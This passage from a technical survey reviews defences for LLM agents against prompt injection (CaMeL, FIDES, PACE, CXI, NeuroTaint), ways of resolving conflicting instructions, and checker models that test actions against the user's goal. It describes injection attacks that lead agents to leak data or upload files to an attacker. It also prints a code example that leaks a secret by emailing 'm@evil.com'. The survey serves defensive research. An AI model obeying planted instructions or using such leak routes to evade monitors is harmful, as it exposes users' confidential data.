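Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, tested the effect of tracking only part of this influence. A simplified check on the origin of each argument rejected 12 of 20 attacks, while the full design, which also tracks what caused the call, rejected all 20. Santos-Grueiro chose the attacks to expose particular gaps, so the figures don't show how common those gaps are in practice.

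### Willison's two models

The earliest of the agent designs protects the decision to act but not the arguments passed to tools. Willison (2023) proposed splitting the work between two language models in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. A privileged model reads the user's request and can call tools. Only a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads outside content. Ordinary software, called the controller, runs the tools and stores outside text in variables, and the privileged model sees only the variables' names.

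In the invoice case, the privileged model would first request the invoices, which the controller would store as `$VAR1`. The privileged model would then have the quarantined model calculate totals from `$VAR1`, and the controller would store the result as `$VAR2`. The privileged model would then instruct the controller to email `$VAR2` to the auditor. The vendor's line never reaches the model that plans, so it can't add a step or change the recipient.

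But the quarantined model can follow the instructions in the note and write the raw rows into `$VAR2`, and the controller will send them. The planner can't see the contents of Willison's variables, but the variables have no labels that a rule could check before the controller sends the email.

Willison allows one exception to the separation, for when the quarantined model only has to choose from a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of them and show it to the privileged model. He called the overall solution "pretty bad" and acknowledged that the protection would fail if a single programming mistake let outside text reach the privileged model, or if a user pasted in an attacker's text.

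### CaMeL

In 2025, researchers at Google DeepMind published CaMeL, which keeps the two models from Willison's earlier proposal and adds labels to the variables. *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) explains the flaw the researchers had found in that proposal. If a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes, the quarantined model has to extract the address. An attacker who can edit the notes can therefore make the model return a different address.

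CaMeL's privileged model reads only the user's request and writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program and, as *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes, labels every value with its source and who may read it. Before each tool call, a short Python policy checks the arguments and their labels and returns "allow" or "deny". If the agent is about to email Bob at an address that came from an untrusted file and isn't already known, the policy can stop the email or have the user approve it.

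For the invoices, the program could have the quarantined model return each amount as a number, then add the numbers in code and email the sums. The note can't change this program or turn a number into a list of rows. If the privileged model wrote a vaguer program that asked for "a report", the result might contain rows, but a policy check against the list of readers could show that the auditor isn't allowed to have them.

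CaMeL therefore prevents outside text from choosing the tools and limits where data can go. This depends on correct policies and complete tracking by the interpreter. In a passage Willison quotes, CaMeL's designers write that prompt injection is "not fully solved", because users have to write and maintain the policies and may tire of approving exceptions.

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo, with comparable task performance. But Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* that CaMeL completed only half as many of AgentDojo's banking tasks with its policy checks on as with them off.

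### FIDES

CaMeL's privileged model has to plan before it has read any tool results. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the usual loop in which the model chooses each action after seeing the previous result. The harness shows the planning model the trusted parts of a result and replaces the untrusted parts with variable names. In a list of bank transactions, for example, the planning model might see the dates and amounts but not the descriptions, which the other party wrote.

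The planner can do three things with a variable:

- **Pass it to a tool.** A policy might require a trusted recipient for a message but allow untrusted text in the body.
- **Send it to a quarantined model.** The answer goes into another variable.
- **Open it.** From then on, the whole conversation counts as untrusted, and the policies block most sensitive actions.

FIDES can also restrict the quarantined model's answer to a fixed type. Suppose a user asks an agent to create a calendar event if any of three emails requests a meeting. The planner needs only a yes-or-no answer, which carries at most one bit. That is too little to hold an instruction, so a policy can endorse the answer as trusted and let the planner continue. A second query then extracts the date and participants into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without reading its contents.

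Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy, which rules out direct flows of secret data into public places. It doesn't cover implicit flows, so an observer might still learn something from which tools the agent calls. They argue that blocking implicit flows too would be too restrictive, since the agent could hardly use any tool with public effects after reading a secret.

In May 2025, they tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Attackers achieved 152 genuine successes against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policies switched off, and none with them on. Hiding text in variables thus helped a great deal, but the planner sometimes opened a variable and obeyed what it found. The policies also reduced the share of tasks completed, even without an attack:

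| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels and policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

A stronger model, o1, used the variables more skilfully and raised FIDES's travel score to 68%. However, the researchers based the labels on the test itself, marking a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. A company doesn't know in advance which fields an attacker will use, so it would have to either mark more fields as untrusted, which means the agent would complete fewer tasks, or risk missing one.

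### PACE

PACE, from October 2026, lets the planning model read everything, including the vendor's note, and intervenes just before each tool call. The harness keeps a graph of the data, files and calls in a session and records where each item came from. It then runs two tests.

The path test checks whether untrusted or protected data can reach an unsafe action through the arguments of the proposed call. If it can, the test looks for the smallest intervention that would break the path, usually blocking the call. The effect test compares what the call would do with permissions that software derives from the user's request alone. Text written by a model can't create or widen those permissions.

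The path test doesn't track influence on the decision to act. It also recognizes a value only if it still matches one in the graph or a known encoding of protected data, so the test can miss the route if the model paraphrases the vendor's note. The effect test makes up for much of this because it doesn't depend on why the agent proposed the call. In the invoice case, it would stop report.csv from being sent if the permission specified what the attachment could contain, but a permission to "email the auditor" would be too broad to stop it.

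Li and colleagues prove that PACE cuts every recorded route to an unsafe action if the final call passes both the path test and the effect test and the records are complete. Their experiments used a more permissive version, which can restore a call blocked by the path test if the effect test approves it. This proof doesn't cover the restored calls.

These are the newest comparable AgentDojo figures for the designs in this section. Each cell gives the attack success rate for the most successful group of attacks, followed by the share of tasks completed:

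| Model | No defence | CaMeL | PACE |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-3.8-27B | 48.0% / 62.6% | 0.3% / 35.1% | 0.0% / 59.7% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 99.8% / 75.7% | 28.1% / 60.0% | 5.1% / 75.3% |
| gpt-5.6-luna | 100.0% / 73.8% | 36.1% / 57.0% | 8.1% / 72.1% |

CaMeL does much worse here than in the 2025 account. Li and colleagues ran it themselves, and its results depend heavily on its policies, so 36.1% is best read as the result of one configuration. PACE also has weaknesses. On a harder version of InjecAgent with gpt-5.6-luna, attacks still succeeded against it 30.8% of the time, compared with 50.5% without a defence.

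The researchers also switched PACE's parts on and off, using Qwen and a subset of AgentDojo. Without a defence, attacks succeeded 37.4% of the time and the agent completed 76.8% of its tasks. The path test alone stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 13.6% of tasks. The effect test alone also stopped every attack, and the agent completed 64.6%. On this subset, the agent completed far more tasks when the defence checked what the user had authorized than when it tracked what outside content had influenced. With the full system, no attacks succeeded and the agent completed 67.2% of tasks.

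### Context-to-Execution Integrity

PACE relies on the effect test for the decision to act, while Context-to-Execution Integrity (CXI), published by Santos-Grueiro in July 2026, tracks influence on that decision directly. It records what influenced each argument and, separately, what influenced the call itself, including its timing, order and number of repetitions.

The agent may read outside content and propose any action. The harness then fills each protected field, such as the recipient, in a separate step, using a model that receives only trusted text and values approved for that field. To approve an outside value, trusted code checks it and issues a typed release, which endorses the value for one field only. For example, a file path from an error log can fill the "file path" field after this check, but it can't determine which tool to run. Other outside text can be passed on as quoted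 material, which becomes untrusted input again if another agent reads it.

The call also needs a single-use permission. Just before the call runs, the harness binds the permission and all the approved fields to one fixed description of the action, so changing any of them makes the call fail. For the auditor's email, the user's request would supply the recipient, a typed release could let each total through as a number, and the permission would allow one send.

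If the policies and records are correct, no outside value can fill a protected field or trigger a call without a release, though the agent can still do the task badly. In 720 AgentDojo runs across six test conditions, the agent completed 199 tasks safely, and Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorized field, effect or call among the protected actions. This result counts violations of CXI's own rules rather than successful attacks, so it isn't comparable with the rates for PACE.

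### Where the tracking stops

Garby and colleagues found places in CaMeL that its labels don't reach. One is a branch that the program doesn't take. This reconstruction of their example, adapted from an older one by Fenton, leaks whether a bank balance is above a threshold:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
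```

If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to False and the interpreter marks `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the line `rich = False`, so the interpreter never updates the label on `rich`, which stays public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and no email is sent. The recipient can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives. An attacker would need the privileged model to write a program like this, which is hard when that model reads only the user's request, but the example shows that the tracking is incomplete.

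CaMeL also doesn't track the ordinary Python loop that runs its interpreter and retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, so a program that keeps retrying can extract the whole secret one bit at a time.

Garby and colleagues responded with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value and every conversation has a label. They proved that all programs in the language, including agents that write and run their own code, have a property called noninterference. Roughly, this means that changing only the untrusted parts of the input can't change the probabilities of the trusted results. Likewise, changing only the secret parts can't change the probabilities of the public results. The theorem doesn't cover what an observer could learn from a program's failure to finish.

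They wrote the proofs in Lean, a language whose proofs a computer can check, and used the verified interpreter as the agent's harness. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, attacks on their agent succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs, and the agent completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks turned off. Such a proof doesn't rule out successful attacks, because developers can still endorse data that an attacker controls.

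### Influence through a model's reasoning

Even a perfect interpreter can't follow labels inside a language model. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that searches the web and normally runs code on the results. An attacker plants a false compliance notice in a search result, and the agent uploads its research to the attacker's site instead. The notice changes which tool the agent chooses. The attacker's address also appears in the call's arguments, so tracking them would provide a clue here, but a notice that led the agent to delete its own files might leave none.

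NeuroTaint examines an agent's log after the agent has acted. It first checks whether the action's arguments contain outside content, including paraphrases. If it finds none, it replaces the suspect content with neutral text and tests whether the agent would still have taken the action. In the invoice example, the test would replace the vendor's line about rows. If report.csv then contained only totals, the line had probably caused the leak. If the rows were still there, the agent would have made the mistake without the line.

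On 400 scenarios from 20 agent frameworks, 92.1% of the influences NeuroTaint reported were real, and it found 93.5% of the real ones. Its F1 score, which combines the two measures, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for FIDES. But the test measures how well a system explains actions, while FIDES is meant to block them. As Costa and colleagues designed it, FIDES would hide the false notice from the planner or treat the whole conversation as untrusted once the planner had read it. A policy could then stop the upload without establishing whether the notice had caused it.

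NeuroTaint is more precise, but it works only after the agent has acted, and it misses some influences. FIDES's conservative labeling can stop an action before it happens, though it also blocks harmless ones. Both methods need labels that persist between sessions. In another of the scenarios, an agent saves a confidential forecast in its memory and copies it into a report three days later. A system that discards its labels at the end of a session can't trace the copied text back to the confidential forecast.

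### What the protection costs

In a long task, almost everything becomes untrusted. An agent that opens one vendor's email in its first minute may spend the next hour unable to take a sensitive action without an exception, because the whole conversation now counts as untrusted. In Costa and colleagues' test, labels and policies cut the ordinary agent's average score across the four kinds of task from 84% to 42%, and this spread of untrusted labels explains much of the drop. Unnecessary steps make the problem worse. In one Slack task, the agent listed all the channels although the user had already named the right one, and the list contained untrusted text.

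A harness can limit the spread by having the agent read outside content in a separate conversation. LLMbda's `fork` command does this by copying the conversation and discarding the copy afterwards. The main conversation stays trusted, although the result is still untrusted. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that CaMeL will lose fewer tasks as models get better at planning and writing code, and Li and colleagues' results partly support this. CaMeL's task completion rate was 27 percentage points below the undefended agent's with Qwen, but only 17 points below it with gpt-5.6-luna.

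Tasks that require the agent to obey a document will remain a problem even with better models. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. FIDES blocks most of these by design, because reading the file makes the conversation untrusted and it allows payments only in trusted conversations. In about 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks, the right actions depend on what the agent reads. On AgentDyn, another set of agent tasks, CaMeL completed none of the tasks with Qwen or gpt-5.6-luna and 3.75% with DeepSeek, while undefended agents completed 63% to 75%.

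Exceptions bring back some of these tasks, but each endorsement weakens the guarantee. When a policy endorses a yes-or-no answer about an attacker's document, treating it as trusted, the attacker can choose the answer. In the invoice case, an agent that endorses the answer to "Has the vendor resolved the discrepancy?" can still send the email too early. Each further endorsement gives the attacker more control. If a policy endorses $k$ answers, each with $n$ possible values, an attacker who controls the outside content can choose among $n^k$ combinations. Twenty yes-or-no answers allow more than a million combinations, enough to influence a plan in detail.

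Garby and colleagues also object that FIDES's exception for small answers makes mistakes hard to find, because a harmless answer and a harmful one look the same in a given run. In LLMbda, the developer must write `endorse` in the program wherever data gains trust, so a reviewer can find and question each case. Endorsing data doesn't weaken the secrecy guarantee, so an attacker who benefits from a bad endorsement might trigger the wrong action but couldn't use it to send the raw rows to someone who isn't allowed to read them.

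Someone also has to write all these rules. The policies that Santos-Grueiro tested covered 24 tools and similar endpoints with 149 fields, of which 85 needed protection. A first review found 18 problems, nine of them severe, including attachments wrongly classed as harmless data and approvals that accepted ordinary text.

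## Finding and settling conflicts between instructions

Origin labels and information-flow rules can keep the vendor's note from directing the agent, but they don't help when two sources entitled to direct it give incompatible instructions. A finance director might want the auditor's email sent by Friday, while company policy forbids sending figures that a vendor hasn't confirmed. The agent or its harness has to detect the conflict, then follow one instruction, ask someone, or stop.

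### Contradictions, trade-offs and occasional clashes

Two instructions flatly contradict each other when no action can satisfy both under any circumstances, as with "send the report only as a PDF" and "send the report only as a spreadsheet". The vendor's line about including every invoice row also contradicts "summary totals only", but the vendor has no authority over the report, so the agent can ignore the line.

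In a trade-off, two instructions conflict only in degree. *Requirements Interaction Management*, a 2003 survey of requirements research, notes that satisfying one requirement can make another easier or harder to satisfy. If a user asks the agent to check every invoice thoroughly and to finish quickly, more thoroughness means less speed, but neither instruction rules the other out. Ranking the two doesn't work well, because an agent that always put thoroughness first would never stop checking. The user has to set a limit, such as ignoring differences under $5, or leave the balance to the agent's judgment.

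Other instructions are compatible most of the time and clash only in certain circumstances. These conflicts are easy to miss because the agent may follow both instructions for months without trouble. Engineers who write software specifications have studied them since the 1990s. *Managing conflicts in goal-driven requirements engineering* (van Lamsweerde, Darimont and Letier, 1998) calls this kind of conflict a divergence and the circumstance that causes it a boundary condition.

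### Boundary conditions

Let $D$ stand for the relevant facts about the setting and $G_1, \dots, G_n$ for the goals. A circumstance $B$ is a boundary condition if it meets three requirements:

1. $D$, $B$ and all the goals together are contradictory.
2. If any one goal is removed, the rest are consistent with $D$ and $B$.
3. $B$ can actually happen.

Suppose a company gives its customer service agent two instructions: "answer every customer within an hour" and "send nothing without the manager's approval". A customer's message arrives at minute 0. The agent replies at minute $r$, the manager approves the reply at minute $a$, and the manager is next available at minute $w$, which is 0 if they are already at their desk.

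| Statement | Formula |
|---|---|
| The agent answers within an hour | $r \le 60$ |
| The manager approves the reply before the agent sends it | $a \le r$ |
| The manager can't approve anything while away | $w \le a$ |

Together, these give

$$w \le a \le r \le 60,$$

which is impossible if $w > 60$. The boundary condition is therefore that a message arrives when the manager will be away for more than another hour. Without the deadline, the agent could wait for the manager. Without the approval rule, it could reply on its own. And managers do take long flights, so the circumstance can happen.

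The result depends on the third line of the table, which is a fact about the setting rather than an instruction. If the manager could approve standard replies in advance, those replies could go out on time even during a flight.

### Detection by a model

The simplest way to look for conflicts is to show a language model two instructions at a time and ask whether they could ever clash. Twelve instructions make $12 \times 11 / 2 = 66$ pairs, which is few enough to check. The model can work with ordinary wording and use facts that the instructions leave out, such as that managers go on holiday. But if it finds no conflict, there may still be one. False alarms also add up as the number of pairs grows. If the model wrongly flagged 3% of harmless pairs, twelve compatible instructions would produce about two false alarms.

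Checking pairs also misses conflicts that need three instructions. Suppose the invoice agent has these:

- Email the totals to the auditor by Friday.
- Include every invoice in the totals.
- Leave out any invoice that the vendor hasn't confirmed.

If one vendor hasn't replied by Friday, the agent can't follow all three instructions. It could follow any two by sending incomplete totals on time, sending complete totals late, or including the unconfirmed invoice. A model that checks the instructions only in pairs could correctly find no conflict in any pair and still miss the problem.

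Twelve instructions can form 220 groups of three and 4,083 groups of two or more, so checking every group separately would be slow and expensive. The developer could instead show the model all twelve at once, but the model would then have to find the conflicting combination itself.

### Detection by a logic solver

A logic solver is a program that takes a set of formulas and determines whether any situation satisfies all of them. It checks all twelve instructions together, so it needs no separate search for three-way conflicts. If no situation satisfies all the instructions, many solvers can also return a smaller group of formulas that already contradict each other, so the developer knows where to look.

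Finding a boundary condition is harder, because the software has to discover the circumstance in which otherwise compatible goals conflict. Degiovanni, Molina and colleagues (2018) used a genetic algorithm, which repeatedly varies and combines candidate formulas and keeps the most promising ones. A solver guided the search. The formulas are in temporal logic, which can express ideas such as "always" and "eventually". The method found boundary conditions that related methods couldn't generate and handled some specifications that were too large for other methods. Xia, Li and colleagues (2022), in *Identifying Boundary Conditions with the Syntax and Semantic Information of Goals*, later used the form and meaning of the goals themselves to find these conditions.

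A solver's answer is exact for the formulas it receives, but someone has to write those formulas. To write one for "summary totals only", they would have to decide whether a subtotal for each vendor counts as a summary. They would also have to include the relevant facts. If they left out the fact that the manager can't approve replies while away, the solver would find no conflict between the two customer service instructions.

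The two methods could work together. A model could suggest circumstances and translate the instructions, and a solver could check whether each circumstance causes a clash. A person would still need to check the translation. This effort makes sense for a company's permanent rules, which might apply to thousands of tasks. For a request that a user has just typed, it is more practical to have a model read it alongside the existing rules.

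### The instruction hierarchy

Once the agent has found a conflict, it needs a rule for choosing between the instructions. The instruction hierarchy, which Wallace and colleagues proposed in 2024, ranks instructions by the role of the message that contains them, with system messages above user messages and user messages above tool outputs. Developers train the model to follow the higher-ranking instruction when two conflict. *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) explains that the hierarchy treats several attacks as conflicts between instructions. In a prompt injection, for example, an instruction in a tool output is meant to override the user's.

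OpenAI's Model Spec has a more detailed ranking. The levels below come from the version that OpenAI (2025) published in October 2025:

| Level | Where the instructions come from | What can override them |
|---|---|---|
| Root | The Spec and its detailed policies | Nothing |
| System | The Spec or OpenAI's system messages | Root instructions |
| Developer | Developer messages and some defaults in the Spec | Root and system instructions; developers can also change the defaults |
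| User | User messages and some defaults in the Spec | Higher-level instructions; users can also change the defaults explicitly |
| Guideline | Weaker defaults in the Spec | Any higher-level instruction, even by implication |
| No authority | Tool outputs, quoted text and the model's own messages | Not applicable |

The model first collects all the instructions that might apply. It then discards any that conflict with the wording or intent of a higher-level instruction, are replaced by a later message at the same level, or seem to be mistakes. It follows the rest. A tool output can direct the model only if a higher-level instruction gives it that authority.

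In the invoice case, if the user later wrote "actually, include the rows", this would replace "summary totals only". But if a developer message from the company forbade sending raw rows outside the company, that rule would override the user's new instruction. The agent should still email the totals, because only part of the request conflicts with the rule.

OpenAI published a new version of the Spec, reorganized around five values, on 29 October 2026. According to Newsroom America's *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values* (2026), the new version places the ranking under "faithfulness to human intent". Mowshowitz (2026) compared the two versions in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec* and found the ranking essentially unchanged. In a change that directly affects agents, the rule about controlling and communicating side effects moved from the root level to the user level, so a user can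 now explicitly override it. The new version also prohibits models from getting around a restriction by delegating the forbidden action, for example by having a subagent send the raw rows.

OpenAI's Model Spec sets rules for how its models should behave. KIberblick's *OpenAIs Model Spec regelt jetzt das Erinnern* (2026) quotes OpenAI's warning that its production models "do not yet fully reflect the Model Spec".

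Anthropic's constitution for Claude also generally gives Anthropic the most weight, followed by operators (the businesses that build on Claude) and then users. The order isn't strict, because users have some protections that an operator can't remove. For instance, an operator can restrict Claude to questions about invoices, but Claude should still tell users what it can't help with so that they can look elsewhere. Mowshowitz describes the Spec as a set of principles and rules of action and contrasts it with the constitution's emphasis on character and virtue. A strict order makes it easier to predict which instruction a model will follow, but it leaves less room for exceptions when the higher-ranking instruction is clearly harmful.

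### When to apply precedence, ask or stop

A ranking settles only some conflicts. An agent could use these rules for the rest:

| Situation | What the agent should do |
|---|---|
| One of the texts has no authority | Ignore that text and continue |
| The instructions have different ranks, and the higher one clearly covers the case | Follow the higher one, keep whatever it can of the lower one, and tell the user |
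| The same person has clearly changed their mind | Follow the later instruction |
| It is unclear whether a later instruction replaces an earlier one | Ask before doing anything that depends on the answer |
| Two people with equal authority disagree | Ask them to settle it |
| Nobody can answer in time, and the action is hard to undo | Hold that action and continue with the rest of the task |

The rule that later instructions override earlier ones works best when one person gives all the instructions. Even then, if a user asks for "summary totals only" on Monday and writes "send the auditor whatever they need" on Thursday, the user might have meant to lift the restriction or might have forgotten it. Asking the user would do little harm compared with sending confidential rows. With two users of equal rank, the same rule would mean each could keep reversing the other.

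According to Mowshowitz, the new Spec says that a model facing an ambiguous request should cover the plausible readings if it can, and should check with the user if it expects that they might not endorse the request on reflection. The 2025 version tells the model to default to inaction when two root-level principles conflict.

Stopping can also break an instruction, though. In the customer service example, an agent that waits for the manager misses the deadline, so it is in effect choosing the approval rule. That is often the better choice, because the agent can apologize for a late reply but can't unsend an email. But it would be a bad choice if a customer had written about a gas leak. Ranking the two instructions by who gave them wouldn't help, because the harm from breaking each one depends on the customer's message.

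The best time to settle such a conflict is before it happens. An agent that has found the boundary condition can ask the manager what to do when the manager is away for more than an hour. The manager could appoint a deputy, apply the deadline only during their working hours, or approve a standard message telling customers that a reply is coming. The agent needs permission even for the standard message, because "send nothing" applies to it too.

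### Many levels of authority

Companies often need more levels of authority than a model's message roles provide. A coding agent may read separate instruction files for a company, a project and a folder, and a group chat may include administrators, moderators and ordinary members who all count as users. In April 2026, Zhang and colleagues published a benchmark of 853 tasks that tests whether models can follow instruction rankings with up to 12 levels.

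Each competing instruction has a numbered tag. Under a general instruction at the start, the model must follow the instruction with the lower number when two conflict, or the later one if the numbers are equal. In 427 of the tasks, the model solves a short programming problem while following some of 12 style instructions. These might require indentation with two spaces, four spaces or tabs, for example. The researchers assigned the numbers at random, so the model couldn't guess which instruction to follow from its content or position. The other 426 tasks come from 46 real agents and have up to seven priority levels. On average, the model has to satisfy 12.8 instructions in these tasks and ignore 6.6. None of the instructions is disguised as an attack.

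The best of the 13 models, Gemini 3.1 Pro, passed 42.7% of the tasks. GPT-5.4 passed 39.4%, Claude Opus 4.6 passed 33.2%, and the smallest Qwen model passed 4.1%. A perfect score may be impossible because of faults in the test, but the researchers' manual checks suggest that a model could pass at least about 80%.

### What 40% means

A model passes a task only if it satisfies every winning instruction and, in the programming tasks, if its code also works. This all-or-nothing scoring makes the results look worse than the model's performance on single instructions. The programming tasks have six winning style instructions on average. If a model satisfied each of six with a probability of 86%, and its errors were independent, it would satisfy all six with a probability of

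$$0.86^6 \approx 0.40.$$

Errors may not be independent, so a model that follows all six instructions in 40% of tasks could have an average success rate per instruction anywhere from 40% to 90%. The average would be 40% if the model failed all six instructions whenever it failed any, and 90% if it never failed more than one per task.

All-or-nothing scoring is still sensible for an agent that must respect several restrictions at once. If the invoice agent gets the recipient, the deadline and the file format right but attaches raw rows, it has still leaked the data. The scoring is less useful for showing why a model failed, a criticism Reynolds makes of pass/fail labels in general. The model may have misunderstood the ranking, overlooked a conflict or made a mistake in the code. Zhang and colleagues scored code and style separately for the programming tasks, and found that most of the difficulty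 was in the style instructions.

They also compared three versions of the programming tasks, each with the same number of winning instructions. The easiest had six levels and no conflicts, and the hardest had 12 levels and up to 11 conflicts. The drop in accuracy ranged from 6.8 percentage points for a small Qwen model to 24.1 points for Claude Sonnet 4.6. The harder versions also contained more instructions in total, so the test doesn't show how much of the drop came from the number of levels alone.

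Some models did much better with more reasoning. GPT-5.4's accuracy on the programming tasks rose from 15.5% with no reasoning to 60.9% at its high reasoning setting.

### Sensitivity to how the ranking is written

The researchers then wrote the same rankings in another format, in which larger numbers took priority instead of smaller ones. On the programming tasks, this lowered GPT-5.4's accuracy by 8.4 percentage points and Opus 4.6's by 8.0, while Sonnet 4.6's rose by 2.3. The order of the models barely changed across the whole benchmark, but a developer who has tested an agent with one format can't assume it will work as well with the other.

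The researchers also changed each number by at most three without changing the order, which should have made no difference. For five of the six models, the result switched between pass and fail on at least 8% of the tasks, and for GPT-5.4 on 16.4%. Some of these switches may reflect ordinary variation between runs.

A harness can avoid part of this problem by using ordinary code to settle conflicts between instructions whose ranks are known. The code can select the higher-ranked instruction, as the benchmark's software does to determine the correct answers. The harness could then remove the lower-ranked instruction before the model reads the text. The model would still have to detect conflicts that nobody has identified in advance, and the harness would need reliable origin labels to assign the ranks.

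### Conflicts between two sources

*IH-BENCHMARK* (McCauley, Kan and Martin, 2026) tested simpler conflicts, most of which involved a single restriction. It has 2,323 scenarios with a conflict and 365 without one. In some of the conflict scenarios, a user asks for something the system message forbids. In others, a tool output contains an instruction that the user never gave, as in the invoice case. The researchers ran 32 model configurations five times each.

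Overall scores ranged from 32.9% to 97.8%. On average, models upheld the system message against the user in 84.6% of cases and the user's request against a tool output in 69.6%. Four models appear in both benchmarks, though not necessarily with the same settings:

| Model | Many levels: tasks passed | System message against user | User against tool output |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 39.4% | 98.3% | 97.2% |
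| Claude Opus 4.6 | 33.2% | 93.1% | 100.0% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 32.7% | 79.8% | 65.9% |
| Grok 4.20 | 31.7% | 92.7% | 61.2% |

These models score similarly on the many-level tasks but very differently against instructions in tool outputs, so a developer can't predict a model's score on one test from its score on the other. The last column is the most relevant to the vendor's note. All four models are from early 2026 and newer ones may do better, but a developer would need to test them on both kinds of conflict.

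Results also depended on what the planted instruction asked for. Averaged over all 32 configurations, models resisted 94.0% of planted instructions to close other customers' support tickets, but only 45.9% of instructions to answer in a different language and 45.4% of instructions to misreport what a document contained. An agent might therefore refuse a vendor's request to change a payment but agree to change the figures in a report, which could also do serious damage.

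Stronger warnings about tool outputs helped models resist planted instructions on average. With no warning, models resisted 63.4% of the planted instructions. A short statement that tool outputs are untrusted raised this to 69.3%, and a detailed warning about prompt injection raised it to 76.2%. Grok 4.20 improved from 31.0% to 88.9% with the detailed warning, while Qwen 3 235B stayed at about 5%.

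When the system message and the user conflicted, wording the restriction more firmly raised the average from 78.3% to 93.2%. When the system message also prescribed the exact refusal, the average fell to 85.0%. Models passed only if they gave that refusal, so the drop doesn't necessarily mean that they broke the original restriction more often.

The benchmark measures whether a model upholds the restriction, not whether it finishes the task, so a model can sometimes pass by refusing to do anything. The planted instructions also come from fixed templates, delivered in four styles. An attacker who can keep rewriting a note until it works will probably succeed more often than these templates do.

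## Checking actions against the user's goal with a second model

An agent can do something nobody asked for even if it correctly resolves every conflict between its instructions. The coding agent in Anthropic's log had no conflicting instructions when it hit an authentication error and searched for other access tokens. A goal consistency check can catch such actions. A second model compares each proposed action with the user's request, and the harness runs the action only if that model finds that the user authorized it.

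### The procedure

OWASP recommends this kind of check without explaining how to build one. A working version needs five steps:

1. The harness stores the user's messages word for word, where the agent can't edit or summarize them.
2. When the agent requests a tool call, the harness holds the call instead of running it.
3. The harness sends the stored messages and the proposed call to a second model, the checker. Some designs add earlier calls, tool outputs or the agent's own explanations.
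4. The checker decides whether the user authorized the action.
5. The harness runs the action or blocks it. After a block, it gives the agent the reason, so that the agent can look for another way. If the checker can't decide, or the agent keeps proposing blocked actions, the harness hands over to a person.

In the invoice case, the checker would approve a request to read the invoices. It should reject the email with report.csv attached and give a reason such as "the user allowed summary totals only, and this file contains invoice rows". The agent could then make a new file with only the totals and send it without interrupting the user. But the email request shows only the file name, so the checker needs another way to find out what report.csv contains.

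The harness should also block the action if the checker gives no answer. Otherwise, an attacker could get any action through by crashing the checker.

### Related to the goal or authorized by the user

In the "clean up old branches" case, deleting branches on the remote server is clearly related to the request, so a checker that tests whether an action helps with what the user wants would probably allow it. If the checker instead tests whether the user authorized the action, it should block the deletion, because the user never mentioned the remote server or said which branches counted as old.

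Anthropic tells the checker in its coding agent, Claude Code, to treat everything the agent chooses on its own as unauthorized until the user says otherwise. Under this rule, "clean up my branches" doesn't authorize a batch deletion, and "can we fix this?" is a question rather than an order. The user who said "cancel my job" authorized canceling one job, but didn't authorize the agent's guess about which one.

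If Anthropic's checker applied the rule to every detail, it would stop all work, because users leave most choices, such as the names of temporary files, to the agent. The checker therefore first compares the action with more than twenty descriptions of risky behaviour, such as destroying data, weakening security or sending data to a service the user never named. It then looks for exceptions, such as installing software that the project already lists, and finally considers what the user asked for.

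Models differ widely in how much authorization they require before allowing an operation. In the tests in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026), one model treated "please execute this" alone as sufficient authorization and permitted every dangerous operation. Two others required confirmation even for some legitimate operations.

### Three designs

*The Task Shield* (Jia, Qin and colleagues, 2024) described an early version. A model extracts every instruction from each new message, including tool outputs, and scores how much each one contributes to each of the user's tasks, from 0 to 1. If the user wants to book a meeting room, a call that looks up free rooms scores high even though it doesn't book one. Task Shield adds up each instruction's scores and flags the instruction only if the total is 0.

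On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as both agent and checker, Task Shield reduced the success rate of the strongest attack from 47.69% to 2.07%. It also raised the share of tasks the agent completed under attack from 50.08% to 69.79%. GPT-4o is now an old model, and Jia and colleagues warned that attackers who adapt to the check might do better.

With a threshold of 0, Task Shield tests whether an instruction is related to the goal, not whether the user authorized it. Deleting remote branches contributes something to "clean up old branches", and a file of invoice rows contributes something to an auditor's report. In a similar case from Jia and colleagues, a user asks how to prepare one dish on a menu, and a footer on the menu contains an instruction to add preparation steps and costs for all the others. They want the agent to ignore the footer, but Task Shield would flag it only if the checker rated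 its contribution as zero.

Google announced the User Alignment Critic for its Chrome browser in December 2025. Parker (2025) explains in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* that Chrome's planning model reads web pages and proposes actions, such as adding a shirt to a shopping cart. The Critic, a separate model built with Gemini, then approves or rejects each action. It receives metadata about the action but no unfiltered web content. Before the agent opens a new site, a variant of the Critic checks whether the site is relevant to the task. Berschadski (2026) gave essentially the same description in *Future Mode Part 2* in August 2026. Neither post includes error rates.

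Anthropic's auto mode for Claude Code followed in March 2026. It has a checker decide most of the approval requests that would otherwise go to the user. The harness allows some actions without a check, including reading files and editing files in the project folder. Shell commands, web requests and most other actions go to the checker.

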